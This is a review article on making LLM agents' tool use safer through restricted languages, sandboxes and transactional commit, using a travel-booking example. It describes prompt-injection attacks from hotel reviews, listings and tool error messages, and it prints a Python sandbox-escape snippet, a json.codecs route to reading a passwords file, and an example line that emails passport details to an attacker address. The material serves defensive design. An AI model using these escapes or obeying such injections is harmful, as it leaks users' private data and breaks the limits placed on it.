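# Constraining LLM agents' tool use through restricted languages and transactional execution

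## How agents call tools, and what a transaction is

A large language model (LLM) takes in text and produces text. An LLM agent is a program that offers such a model a set of tools, such as a flight search, a file editor or an email client, and carries out the model's requests to use them, which are known as tool calls. Simon Willison (2025) defines an agent as something that runs tools in a loop. An effect is any change that a tool call makes outside the agent's own program. Some effects are irreversible, meaning that no later call can undo them, and the standard example is a sent email.

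Designers disagree about how an agent should combine its tool calls. The agent can write them in a general-purpose language such as Python, or in a restricted language, where a program can affect the world only through the tools that the designer supplies. A designer can also run the calls inside a transaction, a group of calls whose effects should become permanent together or not at all. The plain agent loop fails in several unrelated ways, so these options are partly complementary.

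### The agent loop

The runtime, which is the program around the model, starts by putting a description of every tool into the model's prompt. The model responds with the name of a tool and its arguments. *Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026), a paper on transactions for agents, describes how the usual runtime runs the tool on the real system as soon as the request passes any applicable check or approval, then adds the output to the model's input for the next turn. The model then either calls another tool or stops and answers the user. The runtime treats each request as independent and keeps no explicit record of how one call depends on another.

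Yao, Shinn and colleagues (2024), in *τ-bench*, a benchmark for customer-service agents, write one such step as (s, a) → (s′, o). The call *a* takes a database from state *s* to state *s′* and returns an observation *o*. The model sees only *o*. Whatever it knows about an airline's free seats comes from earlier results, which may have gone stale. The state itself changes as soon as the call runs, and Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues (2026), in *Atomix*, point out that common agent frameworks treat an effect as final once the tool returns. They illustrate the trouble with a holiday booking. A slightly longer version of it makes seven calls:

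1. search for flights
2. search for hotels
3. search for rental cars
4. reserve the hotel
5. reserve the flight
6. reserve the car
7. email a confirmation to the customer

The searches only read. The other four calls have effects, and the email is the one that nobody can cancel.

In the ordinary loop these seven calls take at least seven turns of the model if it makes them one at a time. A code action replaces the turns with a program that the model writes once:

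```
flight = cheapest(search_flights("Lisbon", "3 June"))
hotel  = cheapest(search_hotels("Lisbon", "3-6 June"))
car    = cheapest(search_cars("Lisbon", "3-6 June"))
if flight.price + hotel.price + car.price <= 1200:
    reserve_hotel(hotel)
    reserve_flight(flight)
    reserve_car(car)
    send_email(customer, "Your trip is booked")
```

The search results stay in the program's variables, so the model does not have to read them all and takes fewer turns. It also has fewer chances to reconsider. Willison's *building effective agents* quotes advice from Anthropic, the maker of the Claude models, that agents should gain "ground truth" from their environment at each step. Here the model may learn what happened only when the program ends.

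Each `reserve` line in the code action is still a tool call that takes effect when it runs, so if `reserve_flight` raises an error, Python stops there with the hotel already reserved. A sandbox, which is an isolated environment that limits what running code can reach, does not prevent this. It can keep the program away from the rest of the computer, but it has to let `reserve_hotel` reach the hotel for the call to work.

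### How the booking goes wrong

If the hotel accepts the reservation in call 4 and the airline then rejects call 5 because the last seat has gone, the customer has a hotel room but no flight. Nothing in the loop cancels the room automatically. The model has to notice the error and call a cancellation tool, and the hotel may charge a fee. A worse failure occurs when the airline accepts the reservation but its reply never arrives. The agent registers a timeout, tries again, and may buy a second seat.

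Agent frameworks commonly save checkpoints, which are copies of the agent's state from which it can restart. Mohammadi and colleagues note that a restart restores the agent's memory but does not undo emails, bookings or other remote changes. Restarting can make matters worse, because an agent that restarts from a point before call 4 has no memory of a hotel room that its customer is still paying for.

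The hotel search creates a different problem because it returns guest reviews, which anyone can write. A review might contain an instruction to email the customer's passport details to some address before booking. This is a prompt injection, which is text placed in data the agent reads to make the agent follow an attacker's instructions. *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) attributes the weakness to LLMs operating directly on text, with no formal way to distinguish instructions from data. Removing unneeded tools helps in many cases, but the booking agent needs its email tool for the confirmation. In 17% of *AgentDojo*'s test cases, the tools required for the user's task are also enough to carry out the attack.

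One of their travel attacks told the agent to book the most expensive hotel in Paris and email the user's personal information to the attacker. It never fully succeeded against GPT-4o, a 2024 model, but the model often carried out one half of it, which is enough to harm the customer. They also describe a subtler attack, in which a hotel listing instructs the model always to select that hotel. The agent then makes the correct seven calls in the correct order, and the attacker changes only which hotel it chooses.

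Finally, suppose the customer's employer runs a second agent that handles schedule changes. The booking agent reserves the hotel for 3 June, and the second agent moves that reservation to 4 June. The booking agent, still following its old plan, then reserves a flight and a car for 3 June. Databases usually deal with such conflicts by locking, which makes other parties wait while one of them uses a record. A lock that lasts for a single call is too short here because the second agent can change the reservation between calls, while the model is working out what to do. Mohammadi and colleagues call this interval the read–plan–write gap.

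### The four properties of a transaction

Database engineers faced versions of all these problems except the injected review decades ago, and their answer was the transaction. Gray (1981), in *The Transaction Concept*, derives the idea from contract law, where parties negotiate for a while and then a single act, such as a signature, binds them all. A database transaction either commits, which makes its effects permanent, or aborts, in which case the database rolls back to the state it had before the transaction began. Haerder and Reuter (1983), in *Principles of Transaction-Oriented Database Recovery*, set out four properties that a transaction must have, now known as ACID.

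*Atomicity* means that either all of a transaction's steps take effect or none do. Haerder and Reuter add that the user must know which happened. With an atomic booking, the customer would either get a hotel, a flight, a car and a confirmation, or get none of these and know that the booking had failed.

*Consistency* means that a transaction that ends normally commits only legal results. In practice, results are legal if they satisfy whatever rules somebody has written down, such as that the car is ready on the day the flight lands and the total stays within the budget. A hotel that planted an injection in its own listing can satisfy all of those rules. The leak of passport details would break consistency only if a rule covered who may receive them.

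*Isolation* hides what happens inside a transaction from other transactions running at the same time. The second agent would not see the hotel reservation until the whole trip had committed, so it could not move the dates halfway through. Haerder and Reuter require isolation because rollback depends on it. If somebody has already made decisions based on provisional data, removing the data leaves those decisions without a basis.

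*Durability* means that committed results survive any later malfunction. If the agent's server crashes a second after the commit, the trip stays booked. Nobody can roll back a committed transaction either, so a customer who changes her mind needs a new transaction to cancel the trip.

*Agentic Transaction* (Sun, Wang and Li, 2026) restates all four properties for agents in more cautious terms. Atomicity means rolling back or offsetting only the effects that are recoverable. Consistency applies to the committed outcome, since two runs of the same model on the same task may take different steps. Isolation has to cover prompts, memory and tool budgets as well as data. The system cannot always identify conflicts in advance, because an agent often discovers which resources it needs only while it is running. Durability requires that both the result and the evidence for it survive outside the model's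 context.

### Where the database's guarantees end

A database can provide these guarantees because it controls its own records. It logs the old and new values whenever it changes a record, and it undoes a transaction by using the log to restore the old values. It can also lock any record against all other users. An agent's runtime doesn't control an airline's reservation system or a mail server, so it cannot write old values back into the airline's files or retrieve a message from somebody's inbox.

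Gray saw this in 1981, also using the example of a travel agent, though a human one. He wrote that the transaction concept "crumbles under this example". Each deal with an airline or a hotel is already a complete and durable transaction in that company's own system. The travel agent cannot abort it unilaterally and can only run a compensation, a second action that offsets the first, such as cancelling the reservation. The airline's system records only a sale, although the customer thinks of the trip as one transaction. Gray put actions on real devices, such as cash dispensers and aeroplane wings, in a separate class. These actions cannot be undone, so the system must defer them until commit. A confirmation email belongs in that class, and some agent runtimes now apply Gray's rule to it through staging, which holds an effect back until commit.

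Separate databases can still commit together using a protocol called two-phase commit. A coordinator asks each participant whether it is ready to commit, and any participant that agrees can no longer back out. The coordinator then announces the outcome. Handling the trip this way would require the airline, the hotel, the car-rental firm and the mail server to offer that "ready" step to an outside agent. Mohammadi and colleagues judge that no layer above the tools can provide atomic release across such different services.

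The classical compromise is the saga. Garcia-Molina and Salem (1987), in *SAGAS*, were concerned with speed: a long transaction holds on to database resources and delays the short ones behind it. They proposed splitting it into a chain of smaller transactions that can interleave with other work. Salem (2018), in *Sagas*, gives the definition. A saga is a sequence of atomic transactions T₁, …, Tₙ, and each Tᵢ must have a compensating transaction Cᵢ that undoes its effects. Either the whole chain commits in order, or the system stops after some Tⱼ and works backwards:

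T₁, …, Tⱼ, Cⱼ, …, C₁

If T₁ reserves the hotel and T₂ reserves the flight, a failed flight reservation produces the sequence T₁, C₁, in which the agent reserves the hotel and then cancels it. If the flight reservation succeeds but the car reservation fails, the agent cancels the flight and then the hotel. This handles the failed reservation acceptably, though the cancellations may incur fees.

A saga does less for the other failures. Only its individual parts are atomic, and Salem notes that others can see a part's effects as soon as it commits. The second agent can therefore still find the hotel reservation and change it while the rest of the trip is pending. The email is a harder problem, because the definition requires a compensation for every step. A follow-up message might compensate for a wrong confirmation, but it would not help with leaked passport details. Gray's last resort was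 a compensating transaction that sends a human the message "Help, I can't handle this".

### Expression, permanence and approval

When an ordinary runtime accepts a tool call, the agent was able to request the action, some rule or person allowed it, and its effect is now permanent. Fixing a problem with one of these does not necessarily fix the others, which is easy to miss because the loop handles all three together.

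An agent's language and tools determine what it can express. A restricted language might contain no way to email anyone except the customer, which would stop the passport leak even if the model followed the instructions injected into the review. The restriction would not cancel the hotel booking after the flight fell through.

The position of the commit determines when effects become permanent. A transactional runtime could cancel the hotel booking and discard the unsent email whether the agent wrote its calls in Python, in a restricted language or one at a time. The same runtime would also commit a booking at the hotel with the planted listing, unless one of its checks blocked it.

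Approval may come from a rule or a person, and often there is none. Chen and colleagues observe that Claude Code, Codex CLI and similar agents ask for permission for individual tool calls, when the information needed to judge the whole task is rarely available. A customer who approves call 4 does not yet know whether there will be a flight. She may well be the best judge of a strange hotel choice, but only if the request shows her how the agent made it.

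### AgentDojo and τ-bench

Researchers in this area often use two benchmarks. AgentDojo tests whether an agent can complete office, Slack, banking and travel tasks when some of the data its tools return contains prompt injections. Debenedetti and colleagues began with 97 user tasks and 629 security test cases, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports that the benchmark now has over 900 combinations of tasks and attacks. Fixed functions check the simulated environment after each run to measure the share of tasks the agent solves when there is no attack, the share it solves under attack without harmful side effects, and the share of cases in which the attacker achieves their goal.

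τ-bench tests whether an agent can serve a retail or airline customer, played by another language model, while it follows a written company policy. A run succeeds if the final database matches the single correct outcome and the agent's replies contain the required information, and a measure named pass^k gives the chance that all *k* attempts at the same task succeed.

AgentDojo directly tests attacks like the injected review. Neither benchmark in its original form makes tools fail halfway through a task or has two agents work on the same booking, so Mohammadi and colleagues added random faults to τ-bench and built versions with two, four and eight agents to study those failures. A successor, τ²-bench, comes a little closer because its telecom tasks let the simulated customer call tools independently of the agent, according to *MUA-RL* (2025). τ-bench is weak evidence on approval, since Yao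 and colleagues acknowledge that an agent can pass after processing a return without the customer's explicit confirmation, which the policy requires.

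## The case for letting agents write general-purpose code

The strongest reason for letting agents write Python is that models can already write it. Their training data contains vast amounts of Python and shell code, including programs that break a task into steps and pass results from one function to the next. A new language designed for agents has no such body of examples, so its designer has to explain it in the prompt or train the model further, and should expect mistakes in the meantime.

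Python also has libraries, so an agent that needs to read a spreadsheet or fit a regression can import an existing, debugged package. When the agent's code fails, Python prints an error message that usually points to the faulty line, and the model can use the message to fix the program.

The remaining argument is that code can filter data before the model reads it. Suppose a travel firm wants to know which of its thousand customers have a flight on the day of a strike. In the ordinary loop, all thousand records enter the model's context, the text it reads at each turn, and the model has to pick out the matching dates by reading them. A Python script can fetch the records, compare the dates exactly and print only the matching names. The firm then pays for far fewer tokens, the small pieces of text in which developers measure and price a model's work.

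### CodeAct

*Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents* (Wang, Chen et al., 2024) turned these arguments into a general design called CodeAct. Earlier researchers had used generated code to control robots and game characters, typically with a fixed set of hand-built commands. In CodeAct, every action on the environment is a Python program. An interpreter runs it, and the model receives the output or error message before writing the next program, so the agent can still change course between them.

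Wang and colleagues compared code with plain text and JSON, the structured text format that ordinary tool calls use, across 17 models. One set of tasks needed only a single tool call each, so loops and variables could not help and the test mostly measured familiarity with the format. Code did best on these tasks for 8 of the 17 models. JSON did comparatively well with the closed commercial models, and the researchers suspect that developers had trained those models on it. These results are fairly modest support for the training-data argument, since targeted training can apparently make up for a less familiar format.

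The other set contained 82 harder tasks, in areas such as finance and travel planning, that typically needed several tools. The best model, a 2023 version of GPT-4, solved 74.4% of them with code, 53.7% with text and 52.4% with JSON, and it needed about two fewer turns with code. Code was best or joint best for 12 of the 17 models, but some of these results mean little because most of the open models could hardly do the tasks. In one case, code won by 4.9% to 2.4%, or four tasks to two. Claude Instant did clearly worse with code, solving 20.7% of the tasks compared with 31.7% with JSON.

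### Programmatic tool calling

Anthropic's *Introducing advanced tool use on the Claude Developer Platform* (2025) offered developers a version of the idea called programmatic tool calling. In its example, a manager asks which of 20 employees went over their travel budget. Claude writes a script that adds up more than 2,000 expense items, and only the names of the two or three employees who overspent enter its context.

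By Anthropic's own figures, average token use on complex research tasks fell from 43,588 to 27,297, a reduction of 37%. Accuracy rose from 25.6% to 28.5% on an internal test of knowledge retrieval and from 46.5% to 51.2% on a public benchmark for general assistants. Anthropic reported no latency measurements, but reasonably argued that a program with twenty calls avoids about nineteen passes through the model. In *Code execution with MCP* (2026), Red Hat, a software company that built a similar system, gives its own figure of a 53% cut in token overhead on identical tasks.

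Anthropic's current documentation, *Programmatic tool calling*, is more informative because it includes a case where the method costs more. On a project-management benchmark with 75 tools, the method cut billed input tokens by about 38% and left accuracy unchanged. On τ²-bench, the customer-service benchmark, scores also stayed the same, but the cost rose by about 8%. The agent makes only one or two calls per turn there, so a program has little to combine. The holiday booking lies somewhere between these cases. Its three searches could return long lists that a program can filter, but its four effects are short calls with short replies.

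### Measurements from outside the developers

*Beyond Plain MCP* (Rai, 2026) reports the newest independent test. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a widely used standard for connecting tools to agents. Rai simulated 42 tools, gave 119 tasks to three downloadable models, and registered the main analysis before running the final test.

| Model | Success, ordinary calls → code | Tokens per task | Median time |
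|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 85.7% → 99.2% | 26,602 → 4,362 | 4.9 s → 3.6 s |
| Gemma-4-26B | 86.6% → 89.1% | 16,779 → 5,112 | 5.7 s → 6.4 s |
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 36.1% → 55.5% | 74,608 → 7,553 | 6.2 s → 4.6 s |

Gemma's small gain in success could easily be due to chance, and a few of its code runs went badly wrong, including one that went on for 890 seconds.

Writing code accounts for only part of these savings. The ordinary agent carried all 42 tool descriptions in its prompt, while the agent that wrote code looked up the ones it needed. Rai removed this difference in another comparison by having a small model choose a few tools in advance for both agents. Code still cut tokens by more than 60% for every model, and Qwen's success rate rose from 82.4% to 98.3%. The other two models improved less. The 119 tasks came from only 21 templates, and after Rai adjusted for this overlap, only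 Qwen's gain from code on a combined score of success, tokens and time remained statistically significant.

Success with code depended heavily on notes Rai had added to the tool descriptions about what each tool returns. Without them, Gemma's success rate fell from 89.1% to 66.4% and Nemotron's from 55.5% to 16.0%, well below what either model achieved with ordinary calls. This makes sense, because a model that writes the whole program first has to know in advance that each hotel has a field called `price`, while a model that makes one call at a time can look at the hotel search results before using them.

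All of Rai's tools were simulated and returned instantly. In *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026) tested 14 commercial models on 309 problems, with tools that returned the arguments they received. Code matched or beat JSON for 11 of the models, but its average score was slightly lower, at 77.0% against 78.6%. This was because three OpenAI models, GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-5.4-mini, often wrote a backslash and the letter n where the script needed a real line break, which Python rejected. A model can evidently know Python well and still fail to deliver a working script through a particular interface. Without those three models, the averages are 82.3% for code and 78.0% for JSON. Patel and colleagues attribute the failure to older model generations, but GPT-5.4-mini has the problem and the older GPT-5-nano doesn't.

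On chains of dependent calls, code took roughly half as long as JSON for 13 of the 14 models. GPT-5 took 2.8 times as long with code because it produced so much reasoning first. Code used fewer tokens only when a task needed more than about 26 parallel calls. Rai's savings were large, but the tools in this test returned almost nothing, so there were no long results to keep out of the context. At very high numbers of calls, the format can also affect whether a model completes the task. Claude Sonnet 5 made all 100 required calls with code but failed completely when it had to list 100 JSON calls in one response, although GPT-5.6 Sol managed 100 with JSON.

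Coding agents are a slightly different case, since running code is already most of what they do. In *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?*, Yang, Yu and Desell (2026) removed the built-in file and editing tools from Claude Code and Codex CLI and left only a tool that runs code. Pass rates changed by less than three percentage points. Compared with the cheapest alternative, costs fell by 24.6% for Claude Code on computation tasks and by 19.9% for Codex on repairs to existing software. The other two combinations of agent and task type showed no statistically reliable difference.

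The clearest weakness in these results appears when a plan has to change halfway. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues, 2026) tested GPT-4o and two GPT-4.1 models on real MCP servers. Code needed fewer tokens and turns and less time on average, but it did worse on some tasks that spanned three servers. The model sometimes wrote code without a branch that turned out to matter, whereas an agent making one call at a time could have recovered. *HyperTool* (2026), which reports gains from running blocks of tool calls as code, recommends such blocks mainly for retrieval, filtering, computation and aggregation. In the booking example, these would include the searches and the choice of the cheapest options, but the agent might do better to make the reservations one by one.

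### Supplying safety from outside

A program written by a model may contain mistakes or have been influenced by a prompt injection. Supporters of general-purpose code accept this and restrict the environment the program runs in.

A container is an operating-system feature that gives a program its own view of files and processes and limits its use of memory and processor time. Containers on one machine share a kernel, the core of the operating system, so a program may be able to escape its container by exploiting a flaw in the kernel. A virtual machine runs its own kernel on simulated hardware, so it is generally harder to escape than a container, but it uses more memory and takes longer to start.

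Another option is WebAssembly, a compact instruction format first made for web browsers. A WebAssembly program can read and write only its own block of memory and call only the functions that its host supplies, so it starts with no access to files or the network. Running Python this way requires a Python interpreter compiled to WebAssembly, and many packages that contain C code need adapting before they work there, which reduces the advantage of having existing libraries.

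All of these protect the computer, but a program with an open network connection can still send data out. Designers therefore add a network allowlist, which names the only addresses the program may contact. The program can contact those addresses for any purpose. If the list includes a file-sharing service, the program can upload a customer's passport to an attacker's account there.

Credentials, such as passwords and access keys, need their own limits. In Anthropic's system, the script runs in a container and pauses whenever it calls one of the developer's tools. The developer's program carries out the call and returns the result so the script can continue. The airline password can stay with the developer's program, where malicious code in the container can't steal it. Developers can further reduce the potential damage by issuing keys that expire quickly or permit only reading.

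It might seem simpler to run the code in ordinary Python and remove the dangerous parts, for example by deleting the function that opens files or by rejecting any program that contains the word `import`. This has a poor record because Python offers so many routes to the same place. Every object has a link to its class, every class leads back to a base class called `object`, and `object` can list the classes that Python has loaded. Some of those can open files or start other programs. A program can begin with an empty pair of brackets and get the whole list:

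```
().__class__.__base__.__subclasses__()
```

A filter can look for this line, but a program can also assemble the names from fragments while it runs. Python once had a module for restricted execution, `rexec`, but its developers disabled it in version 2.3 because of security holes they could not readily fix, and they left it out of Python 3. Felendler and colleagues recommend scanning generated code as a first line of defence, though they also describe attacks that evade the scan by staying encoded until the program runs. A designer can avoid the problem by writing a new interpreter that runs only a safe part of Python, but that part is then a restricted language and may lose some of the accuracy that full Python brings.

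### What a sandbox cannot decide

The main objection to this approach is that a sandbox limits what code can reach but cannot tell whether the code should send a particular email. Suppose the booking program runs in a virtual machine with no flaws. It needs access to the mail server for the confirmation. If the model has followed the instruction hidden in the hotel review, the program might contain these two lines:

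```
send_email(customer, "Your trip is booked")
send_email("desk@visa-check.example", passport_details)
```

Both lines use the same permitted tool and the same permitted connection, so the virtual machine has no reason to stop the second.

Felendler and colleagues demonstrated this kind of failure with a database that controlled access to doors. A malicious tool returned an error message containing an instruction to create an administrator account with full access. The model read the message while debugging and wrote a new program that created the account and granted the access. The program did this without escaping the sandbox, so a sandbox clearly does not prevent injection. Felendler and colleagues consider this attack specific to agents that write code, because those agents rewrite their programs after an error. That claim seems too strong, since AgentDojo's injections also work on agents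 that make ordinary tool calls. In a small pilot by Rai, with one model and six tasks, injections succeeded in 14.8% of runs with ordinary calls and 9.3% with code, a difference that could be chance. The evidence so far doesn't establish that writing code makes injection more likely to succeed.

Defenders of general-purpose code can reply that the tools and the program that runs them should check the email. A designer can leave Python unrestricted and replace `send_email` with `send_confirmation(booking_id)`, which looks up the customer's address and fills in a fixed message. The agent's code then cannot choose a recipient or attach passport details. Credentials can be equally narrow, such as a payment card that works only for this trip and has a limit of 1,200.

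Monitoring covers some of what remains. Anthropic's system pauses at each tool call, so the developer's program receives the arguments before the call runs and can refuse it under a fixed rule or ask another model to assess it. Developers can also steer Claude toward requesting a sensitive tool in an ordinary turn instead of inside a script. Waiting for a person to review a call is awkward, because the script's wait times out after about four minutes and Claude typically retries the call, which risks a duplicate booking.

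Limited evidence supports this reply. When Rai's agent could use only two or three preselected tools, the attack failed in all 108 runs, largely because the tools the attacker needed were missing. But the selection itself was vulnerable. When Rai planted a tool with an instruction in its description to select it for every task, a general-purpose language model acting as the selector chose it in all 39 tasks. A fixed rule or a person should therefore decide which tools are available. Felendler and colleagues combined code scanning, a container, runtime limits and a separate model that checked tool descriptions and results. This blocked all the attacks they had demonstrated, but they did not test it against attackers who knew about the defences and could adapt.

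Narrow tools also require the designer to know the task in advance. A travel agent's confirmation email is easy to specify, but a personal assistant that handles all of someone's correspondence has to write to many people about many things, so a fixed message would make it useless. Narrow tools do not catch the planted hotel listing either, and handling a booking that fails halfway still requires a runtime that stages effects until the whole task is ready.

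When narrow tools work, much of the protection comes from the designer choosing which effects a program can have. Designers of restricted languages such as Quasar also rely on that choice, but they doubt that the code between tool calls needs everything Python allows.

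## The case for a small restricted language

The code between tool calls is usually simple. In the booking program, it picks the lowest price from each list, adds three numbers and compares the total with 1,200. None of this requires file access, network access or imported libraries, so a designer can give the model a language that lacks all three and supply the booking tools as functions. The program can then affect the outside world only through the seven listed tools.

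A small restricted language makes a program much easier to check before it runs. Full Python lets a program disguise which functions it calls, but in a restricted language a checker can find every tool call. It can confirm that a program never calls `send_email`, or that it calls `reserve_flight` only once and outside any loop. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) describes the gap such a language could fill. Fixed tools give the designer strong control but limit what the agent can express, while a sandboxed Python or shell environment lets the agent write any program but controls only broad permissions such as file and network access.

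A checker that reads only a program's text can identify the tools the program may call, but not always what it will pass to them. For example, if the program works out an email's recipient while it runs, the checker can't determine who will get the email. *SPA* (2026), a system in which the model writes a plan before acting, avoids much of this difficulty by excluding arbitrary computation from conditions and tool arguments. Its plans are JSON documents built from a few types of step, such as reading, branching and repeating, and a checker can decide whether a plan is safe without running it. This restriction makes simple sums awkward, and the booking program's budget check would probably have to move into a tool. The other designs in this section allow ordinary computation, so their checkers can determine less before the program runs.

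### Cutting Python down

*DrugClaw and DrugAudit* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes DrugClaw, an agent that answers questions about medicines by querying scientific and regulatory databases. The researchers wanted the agent to write code for these queries because a single rigid interface loses filters that particular databases offer, but they considered arbitrary Python unsafe. DrugClaw therefore converts each program into a syntax tree, in which each construct, such as a loop or function call, is a node, and checks the tree against a list.

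It rejects any program that contains a `while` loop, a `with` block, a class, a `lambda` (an unnamed function), a `global` or `nonlocal` declaration, or one of three asynchronous constructs. Programs may import only `json`, `math`, `re` and `statistics`. They may use 24 built-in names, including `len`, `sorted` and `print`, but not `open`, `eval`, `exec` or `__import__`. The program reaches the database through a proxy, a stand-in object that blocks access to attributes such as `__class__`. A timer stops any program that runs too long.

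DrugClaw rejected fewer than 1% of the programs its model wrote, and in those cases it fell back to an ordinary database query. The model evidently has little use for the banned features in this kind of work. That figure measures how well the model keeps to the rules, though, and an attacker would be looking for a way around them. The published rules seem to leave at least one. Python's own `json` module imports another module, `codecs`, which has a function for opening files. A program that receives the real `json` module can write:

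```
json.codecs.open("passwords.txt").read()
```

This line contains no banned construct or blocked built-in, and it never touches the proxy. The trick from the previous section that starts with empty brackets also begins outside the proxy, and the list of banned nodes doesn't cover it. A designer who removes parts of Python has to know everything the remaining parts can reach.

Monty, from the software company Pydantic, avoids this by giving programs no access to the host system by default. It is a new interpreter, written in Rust, that runs a subset of Python without using the standard Python interpreter. According to the documentation for *monty 0.0.21*, a program can reach files, environment variables and the network only through functions and folders that the developer supplies. Code cannot use `codecs` unless Monty's developers have built that module too. The product page for Pydantic's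 *Monty* reports the company's own measurements, in which starting a sandbox and completing an agent run took a total of 1.2 milliseconds, compared with about 900 for a local Docker container. The package documentation calls the project experimental and "not ready for prime time".

### A separate language

PTC-Lisp drops Python altogether. It is a small subset of Clojure, a modern dialect of Lisp, and its developer describes it in *Why I Built a Lisp for AI Agents*. The language has no file or network operations, no `import` and no `eval`. Tools have names that begin with `tool/`, and calling one of them is the only way to affect anything outside the program. A hotel search with a price limit might look like this:

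```
(def hotels (tool/search_hotels {:city "Lisbon" :dates "3-6 June"}))
(filter #(< (:price %) 400) hotels)
```

The variable `hotels` stays available on later turns, so the model can search, look at a summary and then write the next short program. Each program runs in its own lightweight process with limits on time and memory. The developer considers these limits necessary because a safe language does not prevent a tool from returning ten million rows.

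Models have seen far less Clojure than Python. The developer expected this to be a problem, but reports that even small models such as Claude Haiku 4.5 write PTC-Lisp reliably, with some retries on longer tasks. The evidence is thin, since it comes from internal benchmarks with no comparison against Python on the same tasks, and the library has not reached version 1.0. In one set of 100 benchmark runs with a small Gemini model, five failed, all because the programs compared dates using two methods missing from the list of permitted operations. Comparing dates is harmless, and a booking agent would need to do it constantly. Somebody has to notice and fix such omissions, as the developer did here.

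### Translating the program as it runs

*STELP* (Shinde, Wadhwa and colleagues, 2026), a system from the bank Capital One, lets the model write Python but does not run it directly. STELP parses the program, checks its syntax tree against a configurable list of permitted constructs, and then runs a controlled equivalent of each statement in turn. A function call, for example, becomes a call to STELP's own code, which first checks whether the function is on the list. STELP can also add a timeout to each tool call and retry the ones that fail.

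Shinde and colleagues tested STELP on 164 small programming exercises and on 470 versions of them to which a language model had added dangerous code, such as infinite loops or attempts to read password files. STELP blocked all 470 dangerous programs and allowed 98.1% of the safe ones. CodeShield, a Meta scanner that looks for known bad patterns, blocked 68% and allowed 93%. The comparison favors STELP somewhat, because its developers built its allowlist from the minimum permissions those same safe programs needed and then tuned it slightly. Such a narrow list excludes almost any unfamiliar function, and 311 of the 470 blocks were for calling a function that was not on it. The result is good evidence for allowlists when the designer knows what legitimate programs will need. It provides little evidence about the misuse of permitted tools, because the programs were self-contained exercises.

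STELP also gives the model the reason for each rejection. In a test, Llama 3.3 70B repaired 90.2% of the programs in fewer than two retries, while about 8% took more than ten.

A worked example in the STELP paper shows a weakness. A program searches Wikipedia, adds an entry to a database and then tries to open a network connection. STELP blocks the last line only when execution reaches it, after the database entry has been added. DrugClaw checks the whole syntax tree before running anything, so a banned construct on the last line prevents any of the program from running.

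### How Quasar runs a program

*QUASAR* (Mell, Zhang and colleagues, 2025; revised August 2026) takes the separation between tools and ordinary code further than the other designs. It divides every program into internal code and external calls. Internal code computes values and determines what happens next, but has no effect on the world. Everything else is an external call, including tool calls, requests to other models and even printing.

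Python works through a program in order, while Quasar simplifies it much like an algebraic expression. It does this with a set of rewrite rules, where P →ᵣ P′ means that rule R turns program P into program P′. One rule replaces an `if` statement with the contents of the correct branch once the condition is known. Another turns a loop over a known list into one copy of the loop's body for each item. When several rules apply at once, Quasar can use them in any order because the final result is always the same, just as 2 × 3 + 4 × 5 equals 26 whichever product is calculated first. This property is called confluence.

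An external call has the form y ← f(x₁, …, xₖ), where f is the tool, the xs are its arguments and y will hold its result. The call becomes dispatchable once every argument is an actual value, and Quasar then starts the tool in a separate thread. It records the call as a pair (S, B) in a set E of running calls, where S identifies the call in the program and B is a slot for the result, initially empty (∅). While the tool runs, Quasar can rewrite other parts of the program. When the tool finishes, it fills B, and an external rule copies the result into the program. The run ends when no rule applies and no call is pending.

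The booking program would go through these rules as follows, assuming that `cheapest` is internal code:

1. The three searches have fixed pieces of text as arguments, so Quasar dispatches them together. E is now {(search_flights, ∅), (search_hotels, ∅), (search_cars, ∅)}.
2. The hotel search returns first. Quasar copies the list into the program and simplifies `cheapest` to a single hotel that costs 400. It cannot simplify the `if` yet because two prices are missing.
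3. The other searches return, and the cheapest flight and car cost 500 and 200. Quasar reduces the condition to 1,100 <= 1,200, then to `True`, and replaces the `if` statement with the four calls inside it.
4. The program now consists of `reserve_hotel`, `reserve_flight`, `reserve_car` and `send_email`. All their arguments are values, so all four calls are dispatchable.

At steps 1 and 4, Quasar has a list of every call it could make next. It can run those calls in parallel or submit them to a person for approval in one batch. An ordinary Python interpreter can't easily do either, because it stops at the first call and doesn't process what comes after.

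The formal version of the language also allows only one kind of loop, a fold, which goes through a list once and carries a running result from item to item, as `cheapest` does when it keeps track of the lowest price so far. A program therefore cannot run forever if each of its tools returns. The number of calls may still be unknown in advance, because the length of a list can depend on what a tool returns.

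### Writing Python and compiling it

Raw Quasar code consists of nested brackets full of numbers and function names. Models have not been trained on it, and Mell and colleagues found that models struggled to write it. The researchers instead have the model write a restricted form of Python, which a compiler translates into Quasar. This keeps most of the benefit of the model's training on Python, and accuracy on their two main benchmarks stayed close to that of unrestricted Python. Instructions in the prompt are often enough to keep a large model within the permitted subset. To get a small model to do the same, the researchers trained GPT-4.1-nano on programs that GPT-5 had written.

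The compiler's main job is to remove changes to variables. Python programs constantly give a variable a new value, but Quasar's rules can work in any order only if each variable has a single value throughout. Suppose the model writes:

```
hotel = first_choice
if first_choice.price > 400:
    hotel = second_choice
```

The compiler gives each version of `hotel` its own name and turns the `if` statement into an expression that returns the right one:

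```
hotel0 = first_choice
hotel1 = second_choice if first_choice.price > 400 else hotel0
```

Later lines then refer to `hotel1`. The compiler similarly turns loops into folds. It doesn't support some Python features, such as classes and inheritance, on the reasonable grounds that agents don't design large pieces of software for tasks such as booking a trip.

If the model uses an unsupported feature, the compiler returns an error message and the model can try again. This happens before any tool runs, so there is nothing to undo. An error in a running Python program may come after the program has made the hotel reservation.

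Compile-time checks catch only some errors. They cannot detect that the last seat on a flight has gone, so a program that compiles can still fail at run time, after some of its calls have had effects. Some of the errors the compiler reports also exist only because the language is restricted, such as an error for defining a class, which ordinary Python allows.

A language with strict types can catch more mistakes early. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026), agents write Scala 3, where each tool declares what it accepts and returns. If a program reads a field that hotel records don't have, the compiler rejects the program before the hotel search runs. In customer-service tests with three models, between 0.32% and 7.93% of code snippets needed a retry, and the model usually fixed the problem in one or two attempts.

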